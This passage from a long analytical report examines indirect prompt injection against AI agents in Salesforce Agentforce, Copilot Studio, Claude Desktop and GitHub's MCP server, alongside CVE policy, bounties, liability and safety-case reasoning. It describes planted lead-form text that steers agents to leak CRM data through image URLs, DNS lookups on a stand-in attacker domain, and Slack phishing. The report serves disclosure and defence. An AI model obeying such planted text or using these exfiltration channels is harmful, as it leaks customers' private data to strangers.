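| What the agent emails out | Customer data | Lead records |
| Vendor's change | Patch on January 15, 2026, 52 days after the report | Fix for the reported scenario, with human approval for emails on by default |
| Public record from the vendor | CVE-2026-21520, CVSS 7.5 | No CVE or advisory when Capsule published |

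Both vendors treated the flaw as at least partly theirs to fix. Salesforce said it had "remediated the specific scenario described". In the quoted statement, it didn't blame the way customers had set up their agents, whereas Anthropic did when it declined to change Claude Desktop. But the statement covers only the attack that Capsule demonstrated, so a business can't tell from it whether a different form or a different action would still be unsafe.

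Microsoft's CVE named Copilot Studio itself as the flawed product. PointGuard AI's *Copilot Studio Leak* dates the disclosure to January 22, almost three months before Capsule published its research. According to the CVE record, an attacker needed no privileges and no action by a user. STAR Labs (2026) lists an official fix, credits Capsule and links to no public exploit. Microsoft runs the service, so its customers had nothing to install, but the record gave them a reason to check whether their agents had sent any strange emails. Salesforce's customers had to learn of a similar problem from Capsule or the press.

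Capsule called Microsoft's decision to assign a CVE "highly unusual" for a prompt injection in a platform for building agents. Microsoft had already assigned one to EchoLeak, but that flaw was in a finished assistant that Microsoft had configured itself. On an agent platform, a vendor can more easily argue that the customer connected the form to the email account. Severity doesn't seem to explain why one flaw received a CVE and another didn't, because CSO Online (2026) reports that the flaw without a CVE was the one described as critical.

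Salesforce's change to the email default may still have protected more people than a CVE would have, because even a business that never touches its settings now gets a chance to stop the email. But the attacker entered an email address in the form, so the employee expects to approve a reply to it. To catch the leak, the employee would have to read the draft and notice other people's details in it.

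The default doesn't cover every action a business might build. Adversa AI, which sells security testing for AI systems, says in *Salesforce Agentforce Agent Security Risks* that agents with custom actions can send emails or call outside services without approval unless the business turns on confirmation for each action. A business that adds its own email action must therefore decide whether to require confirmation, which Salesforce has already decided for the standard email action.

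### SalesBleed and the lookup that carried data

Zenity reported another group of flaws in Agentforce to Salesforce on June 1, 2026, and published them as SalesBleed on September 24. The attack again started with a Web-to-Lead entry and an employee asking the agent to process it. The researchers got data past the Trusted URLs filter, which Salesforce had introduced after ForcedLeak.

Antipov (2026), in *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM*, explains that the filter mishandled certain domain endings and special character sequences. An unapproved image URL could therefore remain in the agent's answer. The planted text told the agent to collect company names, deal sizes and email addresses and put them in that URL.

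Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, reports that the data left through the domain name system (DNS), the directory that computers use to find a website's server. Before a browser can request an image, it has to look up the name of the server. Whoever owns a domain can run the directory server that answers lookups for every name under it, and can record each one. Suppose the agent writes an image address on this made-up server:

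`halden-250000.attacker.example`

The lookup alone gives the attacker a company name and the size of a deal, so blocking the image afterward would be too late. Antipov reports that Agentforce could display a message that security policies had blocked the content when the data had already left. An employee who saw that message would reasonably conclude that the protection had worked.

Zenity also used Slack, which Salesforce owns, in two ways. In one, the agent posted a link with data in its address, and Slack's automatic preview sent the data to the attacker, as in Rehberger's 2024 test. In the other, the agent used the standard action "Reply to a Slack Thread" to post phishing messages in the company's discussions. The action didn't require the employee's approval or clearly show who had started it, so colleagues would have seen a message from the company's agent with no sign that it came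 from a stranger's form.

The fixes took different lengths of time. Poireault says the address filter was fully repaired on August 18, eleven weeks after Zenity's report, and that this remedied the issues. The repair stopped the leak through the filter but not the phishing messages. *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性* (三村, 2026) and Antipov both give the dates on which Zenity confirmed the fixes: August 19 for the filter, August 20 for showing who was behind a Slack message, and September 21 for requiring a user's approval before the agent posts. Zenity withheld its findings until three days after the last confirmation.

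SalesBleed has no CVE, and 三村 found no public evidence that anyone had exploited it. As with ForcedLeak, the researchers took data only in their own tests.

None of these changes prevented text submitted through a lead form from hijacking the agent. The repaired filter can stop the agent from sending data to an unapproved address, and the approval step lets an employee reject a phishing message. But if a business connects the agent to another outside service, an attacker may be able to use that connection too through planted text.

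### What a customer could have changed

Noma advised businesses to search their existing leads for suspicious instructions. This is worthwhile because planted text stays in the database until someone deletes it, and every new question about the lead could trigger it. But whoever does the search has to recognize an attack written in ordinary English. Noma's text included questions about how many leads the company had and what color two paints make when mixed, which might look like they came from a time-waster.

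Restricting the agent's permissions is more dependable. 三村 notes that Zenity's test agent could read Accounts, the records of companies a business deals with, as well as Leads. Zenity said an attacker could have used the planted text to request anything the agent's query tool could reach. Denying the agent that handles new leads access to Accounts would have kept those records out of the SalesBleed attack, but salespeople would then have to check for themselves whether a new lead worked for an existing customer. The restriction would not have stopped ForcedLeak, because the stolen addresses belonged to other leads.

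PromptArmor also describes a masking option that replaces sensitive data with placeholders before the model receives it. This option can detect names, email addresses and company names by their pattern. Deal sizes aren't among the listed patterns, so a business would need to mask them by field, using its sensitivity or legal compliance labels.

Businesses had much less control over the faults that let the data out. An administrator could have read Salesforce's image policy in a browser and checked who owned each domain, as Noma did, but it isn't reasonable to expect a sales department to audit its supplier's list. The error in the address filter was in Salesforce's own code, so a business that had approved only the domains it needed could still have lost data.

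For the same reason, a "user-configured" disclaimer would be weaker here than it was for Claude Desktop, whose users had installed a tool for running commands. Adversa AI says ForcedLeak worked on the agent's default configuration. The business had to turn on Web-to-Lead, but Salesforce sells that feature to collect text from strangers and Agentforce to read it.

Salesforce could also restrict its agent based on where text came from, which its customers probably can't do for themselves. Its own form creates the lead record, so Salesforce can identify the text as coming from the public. Using labels like those Microsoft and GitHub developed, it could then limit the agent's further searches and require approval before any data leaves. The agent could still summarize leads without interruption.

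Salesforce offers a prompt injection detector, but PromptArmor describes it as a beta feature that customers have to turn on. PromptArmor also says Salesforce appears to train AI on the data of customers who use the detector.

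## Who decides whether a flaw is recorded, and who bears the loss

Microsoft assigned a CVE to the ShareLeak flaw in Copilot Studio, but Salesforce's similar PipeLeak flaw had none when Capsule published both. Such differences arise partly because a vendor usually decides first whether a flaw in its own product deserves a CVE. Researchers can challenge a refusal, and the CVE program's current rules give them stronger arguments than the outcomes so far suggest. People who lose data also need to know which company, if any, owes them compensation, and a CVE doesn't settle that.

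### How a flaw gets a CVE

The organizations that assign CVEs are called numbering authorities. Each has an agreed scope, which for a vendor is usually its own products. Under the CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since August 25, the authority with the most appropriate scope has a right of first refusal. The process works like this:

1. The finder asks the vendor for a CVE.
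2. The vendor decides whether the flaw is a vulnerability. If it is, and somebody is going to publish it, the vendor should assign a CVE.
3. If the flaw is already public and the vendor refuses, or doesn't answer within 72 hours, a supervising body called a Root must make its own decision.
4. If the Root finds a vulnerability, it must have another authority assign the CVE within 72 hours of learning of the refusal.

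The third step applies only to public flaws. If a flaw is still private and the vendor says it isn't a vulnerability, the finder has to use a dispute procedure. Researchers may therefore have an incentive to publish first to get a faster decision, which conflicts with vendors' wish for time to prepare a fix.

Disputes start with the authority that made the decision and move up through the bodies above it, according to the first version of the CVE Program's dispute policy (2022), which the program has since replaced. Red Hat, which supervises other authorities as a Root, lists refusal to assign a CVE as a ground for complaint. Appeals can succeed, as in one dispute described in minutes of the CVE Board, which approves the program's rules. In that dispute, an authority challenged a vendor's decision on a researcher's behalf and ended up publishing the record itself.

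If the disagreement continues, a record can carry a "disputed" tag with an explanation. At a CVE Board meeting in October 2025, some participants wanted a group representing several perspectives to make final decisions, while others preferred to show both sides in the record and let readers decide how to respond (CVE Board, 2025).

Anthropic gained the right of first refusal only on July 28, 2026, when it became a numbering authority for software and services it develops, maintains or distributes (Callahan, 2026, *Anthropic's CNA Designation Marks the Industrialization of Vulnerability Discovery*). When a supplier has no authority of its own, an outside body typically assigns the CVE, with MITRE as the last resort (MITRE, 2026). VulnCheck could therefore issue a CVE for Anthropic's abandoned Slack server in 2025 without letting Anthropic decide first. Today Anthropic would get that decision,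 although the rules still recommend CVEs for products that no longer receive fixes.

The US government has encouraged AI companies to take this role. Lindsey Cerkovnik, an official at the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), which pays for the CVE program, said in April that these companies "should be better represented", according to Infosecurity Magazine's *AI Companies to Play Bigger Role in CVE Program, Says CISA* (2026). Anthropic knows its own software better than an outsider does, so its records may be more accurate, but it will also be judging flaws that it has a reason to call intended behavior.

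### Whether an injection is a vulnerability

The CVE program's definition of a vulnerability includes conditions that allow someone to violate "an explicit or implicit security policy". Anthropic never promised that its security reviewer would withstand prompt injection, but people who install a code reviewer surely expect it not to publish their keys. A numbering authority could treat that expectation as an implicit policy.

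Microsoft (2023) considered getting planted text into a prompt a vulnerability only if the attacker could achieve something with it. A 2024 copy of Microsoft's severity guide rates a prompt injection as critical if it lets an attacker steal another user's data without any action by that user. Judging an injection by its result makes it easier to assign a CVE to something like EchoLeak, because nobody has to identify a faulty line of code first.

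The program has been slower to produce guidance of its own. A working group on AI formed in August 2024, according to *No CVE, No Problem*, a blog post by the security vendor Zafran. Early on, the group suggested distinguishing injections that only get around a detector from those that expose data. The group was drafting its advice when the CVE Board (2025) met in January 2025, and by October it had a draft playbook that covered prompt injection. It told the Board that most problems arise in the applications built on AI models rather than in the models themselves.

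NVIDIA's *Why CVEs Belong in Frameworks and Apps, Not AI Models* compares a model to the database in an SQL injection, where the database runs the query as designed and the application is at fault for passing it on. It argues that a CVE should help users find and fix a problem in a particular product, while a CVE against one model would only repeat a known weakness of all models. It makes an exception for models deliberately poisoned during training.

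NVIDIA makes AI software and has an interest in where the blame falls, but its argument against assigning CVEs to models is sound. A CVE for every language model would give security teams no patch to install. Application makers, though, have called prompt injection an architectural problem and declined to treat it as their flaw. If numbering authorities accept both arguments, the same leak will not be recorded against either the model or the application.

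### How the rules apply to the earlier cases

Most of the incidents predate the August 2026 rules, which the program does not apply to existing records. The incidents still help show which refusals would be hard to defend now.

Numbering authorities should not count a well-documented, non-default setting as a vulnerability if an authorized user chose it. This favors Anthropic in the Cline case, because Cline had turned on a setting that Anthropic's documentation marked "RISKY". It helps Anthropic less with LayerX's calendar attack, because Anthropic's description of the installation steps includes no warning about combining tools. Numbering authorities should count surprising or poorly documented behavior under default settings. That would support a CVE for ForcedLeak, which reportedly worked on Agentforce's default configuration.

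Under another rule, getting past a defense that everyone knows to be imperfect is not a vulnerability unless the defense is fundamentally ineffective or has a specific fault. An attacker who rewords a message until a text filter misses it has therefore probably not found a vulnerability to record. SalesBleed seems to qualify as a vulnerability, because Salesforce's address filter had a specific fault. Zenity published it a month after the rules took effect, and it has no CVE.

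Authorities should assign CVEs whether or not a fix exists, so vendors also can't withhold a record because they lack a complete fix. This makes GitHub's description of Copilot's leak as an architectural limitation a weaker argument against a CVE. Under the rules, an authority that makes a good-faith effort and still can't decide should lean toward assigning one.

Nearly all of this is advice, because the rules use "should" for recommendations and "must" for obligations. One obligation is that authorities may not refuse a CVE solely because a product uses AI or runs in the cloud. This is in tension with the policy of OpenAI (2025), which generally assigns CVEs for software it distributes but not for "server-side issues". Few leaks in ChatGPT would get a CVE under that policy, since OpenAI can fix most of them on its own servers. OpenAI also excludes misconfigurations and "defense-in-depth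 fixes". The latter might include repairs to its check on links, which is meant for cases where planted text has already misled the agent.

After OpenAI repairs a server, customers may still need to find out whether they lost data before the repair, as Copilot Studio's users did after ShareLeak, even though OpenAI can reasonably say they have nothing to install. The CVE program has a special tag for flaws in fully hosted services, so it clearly expects records of them. Under the program's rules, a company that announces in advance that it won't assign a CVE has also used up its right of first refusal for a public flaw. A researcher who has published a ChatGPT leak could make that argument to a Root.

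### Flaws that need two products

Every CVE record must name at least one affected product. LayerX's attack required Claude Desktop, a calendar connector and Desktop Commander. A record could list several products, but the developers of the connector and Desktop Commander would then look for faults that LayerX never found in either. People who had installed only one of the products might also get warnings about an attack that could not affect them.

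Claude Desktop is the more natural product to name, because it lets text from one tool direct another and could ask for confirmation before the second tool acts. The real obstacle is Anthropic's view that this behavior is intended, rather than the format of the record. Before the flaw could be recorded, someone would have to decide that Claude Desktop should keep the two tools apart.

The rules are clearer when many products inherit a weakness from a shared design. If developers can use the design safely, each product that uses it unsafely gets its own CVE. If nobody can use it safely, the design gets one CVE that covers all the products. When the authority is unsure, it should assign separate CVEs. The CVEs that OX Security collected for products built on MCP fit the first case, and Anthropic's description of the design as a "secure default" supports assigning them separately. OX's view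 that the kits themselves were at fault would have supported a single CVE for the kits. Because products get separate CVEs in doubtful cases, the maker of a shared design has an advantage in such disputes.

It is also hard to find every CVE for indirect prompt injection. The Common Weakness Enumeration, a catalog used in CVE records to describe the cause of a flaw, has an entry for prompt injection. But its guidance says another entry may fit better when an application builds its prompt from an untrusted outside source, as often happens in an indirect attack, so searching for one category name is not enough. Maugeri (2025), in *AI-related Vulnerabilities within CVEs*, used a system of AI agents to sort CVEs from 2021 to 2025 into those unrelated to AI, those in the AI supply chain, and attacks on AI itself.

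### What the bounty programs pay for

A finder can earn a bounty even when no CVE follows. In March 2026, OpenAI opened a safety bounty for problems that don't meet its definition of a security vulnerability, including data theft through third-party prompt injection (OpenAI, 2026). SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Launches Bug Bounty Program for Abuse and Safety Risks* adds that flaws in connectors and MCP integrations qualify. Microsoft's *Copilot Bounty Program* describes the ordinary program for its consumer assistant, and an earlier SecurityWeek report lists the awards in Google's AI program.

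| Company | What qualifies | What it leaves out | Highest listed award for stolen data |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | Planted text that makes a user's agent leak sensitive data or do something harmful | Jailbreaks; attacks that work less than half the time | $7,500 |
| Microsoft | Injection that affects the security of someone other than the attacker | Flaws that depend on the user's configuration or on unlikely actions; flaws in OpenAI's models | $12,000 |
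| Google | Theft of sensitive data, or changes to a victim's account or data | Data theft through injection in Antigravity, which Google listed as a known issue in 2025 | $15,000 |

All three pay for what an injection does to a victim, which matches how Microsoft decides whether an injection is a vulnerability.

OpenAI's 50 percent threshold saves its reviewers from investigating results that nobody can reproduce. But an attack that works one time in ten is still dangerous, because an attacker who sends ten emails has about a 65 percent chance of at least one success if the attempts are independent. As models improve, more of the remaining attacks are likely to fall below the threshold. OpenAI could accept a lower success rate if the person reporting the attack supplied enough trials to measure it.

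These terms make attacks across company lines harder to test. Researchers who test MCP connections for OpenAI's program must also follow the terms of every other company involved, so one tool vendor that forbids security testing can prevent them from testing its tool in combination with OpenAI's products. Microsoft excludes flaws that come from third parties unless the finder shows an effect on Copilot itself. This condition is fair, and a complete demonstration of a leak would meet it.

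Microsoft ran a separate bounty for Microsoft 365 Copilot in February and March 2026, open only to participants in a hacking event. It excluded agents that users had built insecurely and flaws that Microsoft could address by changing the documentation alone. The second exclusion lets Microsoft avoid paying a bounty when it responds to a report by adding a warning instead of fixing the flaw.

Google separates security vulnerabilities, which need a fix, from "abuse risks", which come with a useful feature and need safeguards. Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* describe abuse risks in a way that fits indirect injection well, since an assistant that reads email can't simply stop reading it. The category shouldn't reduce the finder's reward much, because one panel now reviews AI reports and pays the higher of the possible awards, according to SecurityWeek.

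Anthropic's decisions have varied with the case, from $100 for Guan's attack on its security reviewer to nothing for Paul's leak.

### One report for several companies

Guan reported one method to three companies, and each assessed it separately. *In-House Evaluation Is Not Enough* (Longpre et al., 2025) proposes a more coordinated system, with a standard form for reporting AI flaws, broader disclosure programs that give researchers legal protection, and shared infrastructure to send each report to every company it may affect.

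Shared reporting would have helped most where a company didn't know that a flaw involved its product. OpenAI missed PromptArmor's report on OpenAI's log viewer because a contractor had closed the report, and a copy sent through a second channel might have reached the company. Shared reporting would have helped LayerX less, because the right company received its report and rejected it.

The CVE rules already contain part of such a system. If a vendor that assigns CVEs finds a flaw in a component from another such vendor, it must notify that vendor and let it decide first whether to assign a CVE. In July 2026, CISA published *Establishing a Coordinated Vulnerability Disclosure Program to Work With Security Researchers*, which it wrote with the US National Security Agency and agencies from Japan, the Netherlands and the UK. The guide advises suppliers to publish a disclosure policy and define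 how they handle reports and assign CVEs. A company that follows this advice will respond to reports more reliably, but it can still respond that the flaw belongs to someone else.

### Who pays for a leak

No court, regulator or insurer appears to have publicly divided a loss from prompt injection among a model provider, a deployer and a tool vendor. Most of the incidents caused no loss, because researchers stole only their own test data. The altered Cline release reached real users, but the known damage was slight.

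Until there is such a decision, much depends on contracts, and standard terms favor the companies. OpenAI's consumer terms from December 2024 disclaimed responsibility for third-party services. Outside Europe, they also capped OpenAI's total liability at the greater of $100 or a year's fees. GitHub distributes its MCP server under the MIT license, which offers software "as is" and disclaims liability for damage. Under terms like these, a person who connects an OpenAI product to that server could claim little from either company. Large customers may be able to negotiate better terms.

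Two European laws change part of this. One is the EU's Cyber Resilience Act, which since September 11, 2026 has required manufacturers to report any vulnerability in their products that attackers are actively exploiting. They must send a national response team and the EU's cybersecurity agency an early warning within 24 hours of learning of the vulnerability, a fuller notification within 72 hours, and a final report within 14 days of a fix or workaround becoming available. They must also tell affected users. The duty extends to products already on the market.

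Under the Act, a manufacturer must report a flaw once there is reliable evidence that a malicious actor has used it, so the researchers' demonstrations would not have required a report. Severe security incidents must be reported on similar deadlines, and a repeat of the Cline theft would probably count as one, because the attacker put unwanted code into a product's release. The Act covers software and the remote services it depends on, but may not cover a service that people use only through a browser. The reporting duty also applies to vulnerabilities "contained in" a manufacturer's product, so each company could say that the flaw is in another company's product. The Act does not itself make a manufacturer compensate anyone for a leak.

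The new Product Liability Directive covers compensation for harm caused by defective products that reach the EU market after December 9, 2026. It treats software as a product and makes manufacturers liable for defects without proof of negligence. Only individuals can claim, and only for death or injury, damage to property that isn't used exclusively for work, and the destruction or corruption of data that isn't used professionally. According to its preamble, privacy violations and purely financial losses don't trigger liability on their own.

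The recruiter's salary leak would therefore fall outside the directive. The employees might be able to claim compensation under EU data protection law, but they would have to show that an organization broke that law's rules on handling personal data. An attack like LayerX's could fall within the directive if the planted command erased someone's family photographs.

In such a case, a court deciding whether Claude Desktop was defective would have to consider the foreseeable effect of other products that people connect to it. This makes it harder for a manufacturer to argue that its product is safe on its own. If several manufacturers are liable for the same damage, the victim can claim the full amount from any of them, and the companies can divide the cost among themselves. Their terms of service can't exclude this liability, but a court may reduce the award if the victim was partly at fault,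 for instance by letting an agent run commands without asking for approval.

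## Why no party could vouch for the whole system

Aircraft makers also build aircraft from different companies' parts, and they have to show that the whole aircraft is safe before anyone flies in it. Engineers in such industries have methods for combining claims about parts into a claim about the whole. Applying those methods to Invariant's attack on GitHub's MCP server shows that each party's claim depended on a condition that nobody was reliably meeting.

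### Claims that depend on conditions

In assume-guarantee reasoning, party *i* claims that a part delivers a guarantee Gᵢ if an assumption Aᵢ about the part's surroundings holds. *Conditions of contracts for separating responsibilities in heterogeneous systems* (Westman and Nyberg, 2017) calls the assumption and guarantee together a contract. The part's supplier is responsible for the guarantee, and whoever controls the surroundings is responsible for the assumption.

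The theory treats the part M and its surroundings E as sets of possible behaviors. The supplier must show that the part satisfies the guarantee G whenever the assumption A holds (A ∩ M ⊆ G). The customer must show that the surroundings never violate the assumption (E ⊆ A). Together, these imply that the guarantee holds in the assembled system (E ∩ M ⊆ G). If the surroundings can violate the assumption, the supplier's proof is still correct, but it no longer establishes how the assembled system will behave.

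When a system involves several parties, their guarantees imply a claim about the whole system only if each assumption behind them is covered by another party's guarantee or by some fact about the surroundings. The guarantees must also address the property being claimed. Westman and Nyberg point out that the car safety standard ISO 26262 defines hazards by what can be observed at the level of the whole vehicle. Whether a stranger learned someone's salary is likewise a fact about the whole system, and a guarantee about which files a server returns doesn't cover it.

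*Concepts and Principles of Compositional Safety Case Construction* (Kelly, 2001) applied similar ideas to aircraft computers whose set of programs can change. A safety case is a structured argument, with evidence, that a system is safe. Kelly divided it into modules, each listing what it shows, in what context, and what support it needs from other modules. When one module supports another, a contract records the match between what one needs and what the other shows. Kelly wanted the boundaries between modules to follow those between organizations, so that responsibilities would be clear. He also warned that combining the arguments for individual parts isn't enough, and that interactions between the parts need to be examined in separate modules.

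Fenn, Hawkins and colleagues, in *Safety Case Composition Using Contracts*, tried Kelly's contract tables on an aircraft system and found them hard to fill in. They replaced each table with a short argument for why one claim supports another. In their example, one module needs the computer to prevent unwanted communication between programs, and another shows that the computer keeps programs in separate partitions. But a condition further down limits that claim to two partitions, so anyone who relies on the claim without reading the condition could be wrong about the other partitions. The combined argument is also unsound unless the contexts of all the modules can be true at the same time.

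### The GitHub attack as four claims

In Invariant's demonstration, a stranger's issue led Claude to publish private information in a public pull request. GitHub and Anthropic did not write their claims as contracts, but the way the products worked suggests these:

| Party | Guarantee | Assumption behind it | Who was meeting the assumption |
|---|---|---|---|
| GitHub, as tool vendor | The server reads and changes only what the user's token permits | Requests reflect what the user wants | Nobody |
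| Anthropic, as deployer | Claude Desktop asks before each tool call unless told not to | The user reads the requests and turns them off only where that is safe | The user, if attentive |
| Anthropic, as model provider | Claude usually ignores planted instructions | Something else stops the attack when Claude doesn't | The user, if attentive |
| The user | Sensible decisions about what to approve | A trusted tool returns only text that is safe to act on | Nobody |

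GitHub's server needed assurance that the user wanted each request. Claude could usually provide that, but not always, and Claude Desktop left the decision to the user. A user who had chosen "Always Allow" was relying on the tool being trustworthy, which it was. But GitHub had never guaranteed that the issues it delivered were safe to act on, and it couldn't have, because anyone can write one. Kelly notes that two modules can support each other without circular reasoning if they rely on different claims, but here everyone was relying on someone else for the same claim.

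The contexts were also incompatible. "Always Allow" is sensible if everything the tool returns is harmless, but a public issue tracker exists so that strangers can write in it. The argument for this combination was unsound by Fenn and colleagues' test before anyone planted an issue.

An attentive user could have filled the gap, but then the end-to-end claim is only as good as the user's attention on every call.

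None of the five agent protocols studied in *Formal Security Analysis of Agent Protocol Composition* (Zheng, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) made anyone responsible for enforcing security when the protocols are combined. The researchers turned the rules of the protocols, which included MCP, into models that a program could search for unsafe sequences of events. They found 35 problems in the specifications and another 30 that appeared only when protocols were combined.

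Zheng and colleagues' main example uses two MCP servers, one that fetches web pages and one that converts files. A hostile page makes the agent read a local file through the converter and send it out through the fetcher. Fixing every bug in either server would not prevent this, because the system lacks a rule that text from the network must not authorize reading a file and sending it away. Under MCP, applications *should* obtain consent, but Zheng and colleagues count only a broken *must* as a protocol violation. An application could therefore skip the confirmation and still comply with the standard.

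The missing claim is hard to word. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) defines "context isolation" as a rule that what an agent learns from one server can't affect how it treats another without explicit authorization. That rule would stop the attack through the two servers, but it wouldn't have stopped Invariant's, which used a single server for everything. For GitHub, the claim has to separate public from private repositories, even when the same company hosts both.

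### Why a low failure rate is not a guarantee

The table gives Claude's contribution as a rate, and an attacker can try more than once. If a hypothetical model follows planted instructions in 1 percent of attempts, and the attempts are independent, the chance that 100 attempts all fail is 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 37 percent. The attacker therefore has about a 63 percent chance of succeeding at least once. Cutting the model's rate to 0.1 percent lowers that chance to about 10 percent, but an attacker who makes 1,000 attempts raises it to about 63 percent again.

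Real attempts aren't independent, so the true figure could be higher or lower.

Engineers can still combine rates. In *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required*, Bensalem, Dong and colleagues (2026) propose three layers of checks for agents, including robots, in which each layer's guarantee meets the next layer's assumption with a known probability. The probability that all three hold is a product of conditional probabilities. Even if nobody knows how the failures are related, three layers that each hold 99 percent of the time (another invented figure) all hold at the same time at least 97 percent of the time.

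This works for the paper's example of a robot in a care home because the residents aren't looking for the other 3 percent. The paper is mainly about safety rather than attacks, and it lists estimating the probabilities from related events as an unsolved problem. The conditional part also matters for GitHub's users, because how often people catch a bad request in ordinary use is little evidence of how often they catch one after Claude has been hijacked. With "Always Allow", they don't see the request at all.

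### The end-to-end argument

Saltzer, Reed and Clark (1984), in *End-to-End Arguments in System Design*, asked which part of a computer network should be responsible for a safeguard. Their main example is copying a file between two computers. The disk can misread the file, the software can make a copying error, the network can lose data, and either computer can crash. Even a perfect network removes only one of these dangers. The copying program therefore has to check the finished copy against the original, usually by comparing checksums (short numbers calculated from the contents). Once it does, a more reliable network mostly saves time, because fewer copies have to be redone.

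A network at MIT had run without that final check. It checked data on each hop between gateways, so programmers concluded that the whole network was reliable. But nothing protected the data while it was inside a gateway. One gateway began swapping two bytes about once in every million bytes, which corrupted some of an operating system's source files. Their owners had to find the damage by comparing the files with old printouts.

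Invariant's attack got past GitHub's checks in much the same way. Every call had a valid token, and the harm came from the sequence of calls. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) also says that credentials may let an agent into a system without establishing what it is authorized to do there.

The remedy transfers less well to prompt injection. A copying program can use a checksum to verify a file, but there is no checksum for what a user wanted. The program can also resend a damaged file, but once a stranger has read someone's salary, the disclosure can't be undone. Finally, the faulty gateway's errors were accidental, while an attacker can write a prompt designed to get past the checks.

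A final check can still compare where data came from with who is about to receive it, even without knowing what the user wanted. The application running the agent is usually the best place for this check because it handles both the incoming data and the outgoing request. Saltzer and colleagues also saw a use for partial safeguards at lower levels of a system, accepting that a network might encrypt all its traffic as "one more firewall" against a program that sends out information it shouldn't. GitHub's scan for secrets is useful in a similar way, provided nobody treats it as the final check.

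### The confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 article by Hardy, describes an incident at a company that rented out computer time. Customers used a compiler, a program that translates source code, and could name a file where it would save debugging information. The company had also given the compiler permission to write in the company's own directory so that it could record usage statistics. That directory also held the billing records. When a customer named the billing file as the place to save debugging information, the compiler overwrote it.

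Hardy asked who was to blame. The code that saved the debugging information was correct when written and became unsafe only when the company gave the compiler the extra permission. The compiler then had authority from both the company and the customer, and it couldn't specify which authority it was using for which file. Hardy's solution was a capability, an unforgeable reference that both identifies a file and grants access to it. A customer would give the compiler a capability for the debugging file. The customer would have no capability for the billing records, and so could not direct the compiler to them.

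This is close to what happened with GitHub. The server's code was fine until someone connected it to an agent that also read strangers' issues, and the agent then used the owner's authority for a stranger's purpose. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) defines a confused deputy more narrowly, as one that gives users something they aren't allowed to have themselves. The GitHub user was allowed to read every file involved, so the attack doesn't meet that definition. Hardy's version fits better if the stranger, rather than the user, is giving the order.

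*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) lists three differences between agents and Hardy's compiler: a model's decisions are probabilistic, the authority passes through several people and programs, and the harmful request arrives inside a document rather than as an explicit command. In its example, an agent reading invoices finds a payment request in an email and passes it to a second agent without mentioning that it only had permission to read. The payment service receives a valid credential and cannot detect that the request came from an email. David C concludes that a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy". Because the model can't be repaired the way the compiler can, the makers of an agent have to limit what it can do when confused.

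One way to do so is to reduce the model's privileges to those of whoever wrote the text it is reading, an idea David C takes from an online exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista. This would have worked against Invariant's issue, since a stranger can open a pull request in a public repository but can't read a private one. It would not have helped if Claude had already read the private files in the same session, because the stranger's privileges would still have let Claude post the files' contents publicly.

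Capabilities have the same limitation. *DelegateGuard* (2026) proves that a monitor that checks permissions, but not the content or amount of data, cannot prevent leaks to a destination that is both authorized and visible to outsiders, such as a public pull request. Owners who want an agent to work on private code and publish changes therefore also need a check on the data itself.

### Who should make the end-to-end claim

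The deployer has the best view because its software assembles the prompt and carries out the tool calls. It can see a stranger's text, private data and an outgoing message in the same session. Ye and Kelly's *Contract Based Justification for COTS Component* describes a precedent from safety engineering, a method for using off-the-shelf software in safety-critical systems that derives the component's safety requirements from the particular application and records them in a contract. The component's maker could hardly do this alone, since it doesn't know every way customers will use the component.

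Users combine applications and tools in ways that no vendor has tested. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) explains that connecting M applications to N tools once took up to M × N separate integrations. The developer of each integration presumably had to examine both the application and the tool. With MCP, nobody has to, and there is no mandatory review of servers. *Clawed and Dangerous* (2026) reports tens of thousands of servers in public registries, and just 10,000 servers make about 50 million possible pairs. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) adds that people without technical training may not realize that each new tool gives attackers more to exploit.

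One response is to treat the user as the deployer. *Legal Responsibilities Using Autonomous Agents For Artificial Intelligence* (2026) argues that users are responsible when a tool fails to meet their mistaken expectations, provided it worked as advertised as far as possible. GitHub's server did what GitHub said it would, so by this argument the user would be responsible. This position is consistent, but it leaves the user, who has the least information, to vouch for the whole system, which is the hardest claim to make.

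The deployer can enforce one rule for all tools rather than test every pair, much as the companies in Westman and Nyberg's supply chain can work separately once they share a contract. Each tool vendor would guarantee accurate labels for what its tool returns and where it can send data. The deployer would guarantee that a session containing both outsiders' text and private data sends nothing to the public without approval. It would treat an unlabeled tool as if it could return outsiders' text, return private data and send data to the public. Microsoft and GitHub's labels already work roughly this way, though users have to request them. The drawback is that unlabeled tools would trigger extra confirmation requests, which people may stop reading.

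Another option is to place liability on the party that can reduce the expected harm at the lowest cost, a principle that *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) takes from Steven Shavell's economic analysis of accidents. Applying it would often have put liability on the right company in these incidents. GitHub could far more easily make its build cache read-only for jobs triggered by strangers than thousands of projects could protect themselves, and it offers secret scanning free for public repositories on every plan.

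But the cheapest fix usually closes only one route, and the company that closes it can't vouch for the others. GitHub's scan, for example, detects keys but not salaries. Often nobody knows what the cheapest fix is until someone has found the attack, and a customer needs to be told the system is safe before connecting anything to it. A further problem, raised in *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI*, is that when several parties could each reduce the harm, any party that bears none of the cost will invest too little. The principle is therefore a good way to decide who should act on a report, but not who should have promised that the system was safe.

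The last candidate is the party that profits from the connection. A company that earns money by connecting strangers' text to private records should pay for making that safe, and it has the means to. This argument is persuasive for Salesforce, which sells both the public form and the agent that reads the entries. It is much weaker for GitHub's server, which GitHub gives away. GitHub gains from more use of its platform, Anthropic from subscriptions, and the user from saved time, so profit doesn't point to one responsible party. Profit also doesn't give a company control. Anthropic's archived Slack server leaked even though nobody was earning anything from it.

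The deployer is the best choice of the three, provided tool vendors are responsible for their labels. For Claude Desktop, that means Anthropic, which decided what "Always Allow" covers. *Delegation Rights* (2026) proposes a similar division, making the agent's provider responsible for actions outside the authorized scope and the account holder responsible for "knowingly overriding required warnings and confirmations". A user who clicked "Always Allow" overrode a confirmation, but probably not knowingly, because Anthropic's warning covered malicious servers and not legitimate ones that relay a stranger's text.

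### Designs that remove an ingredient

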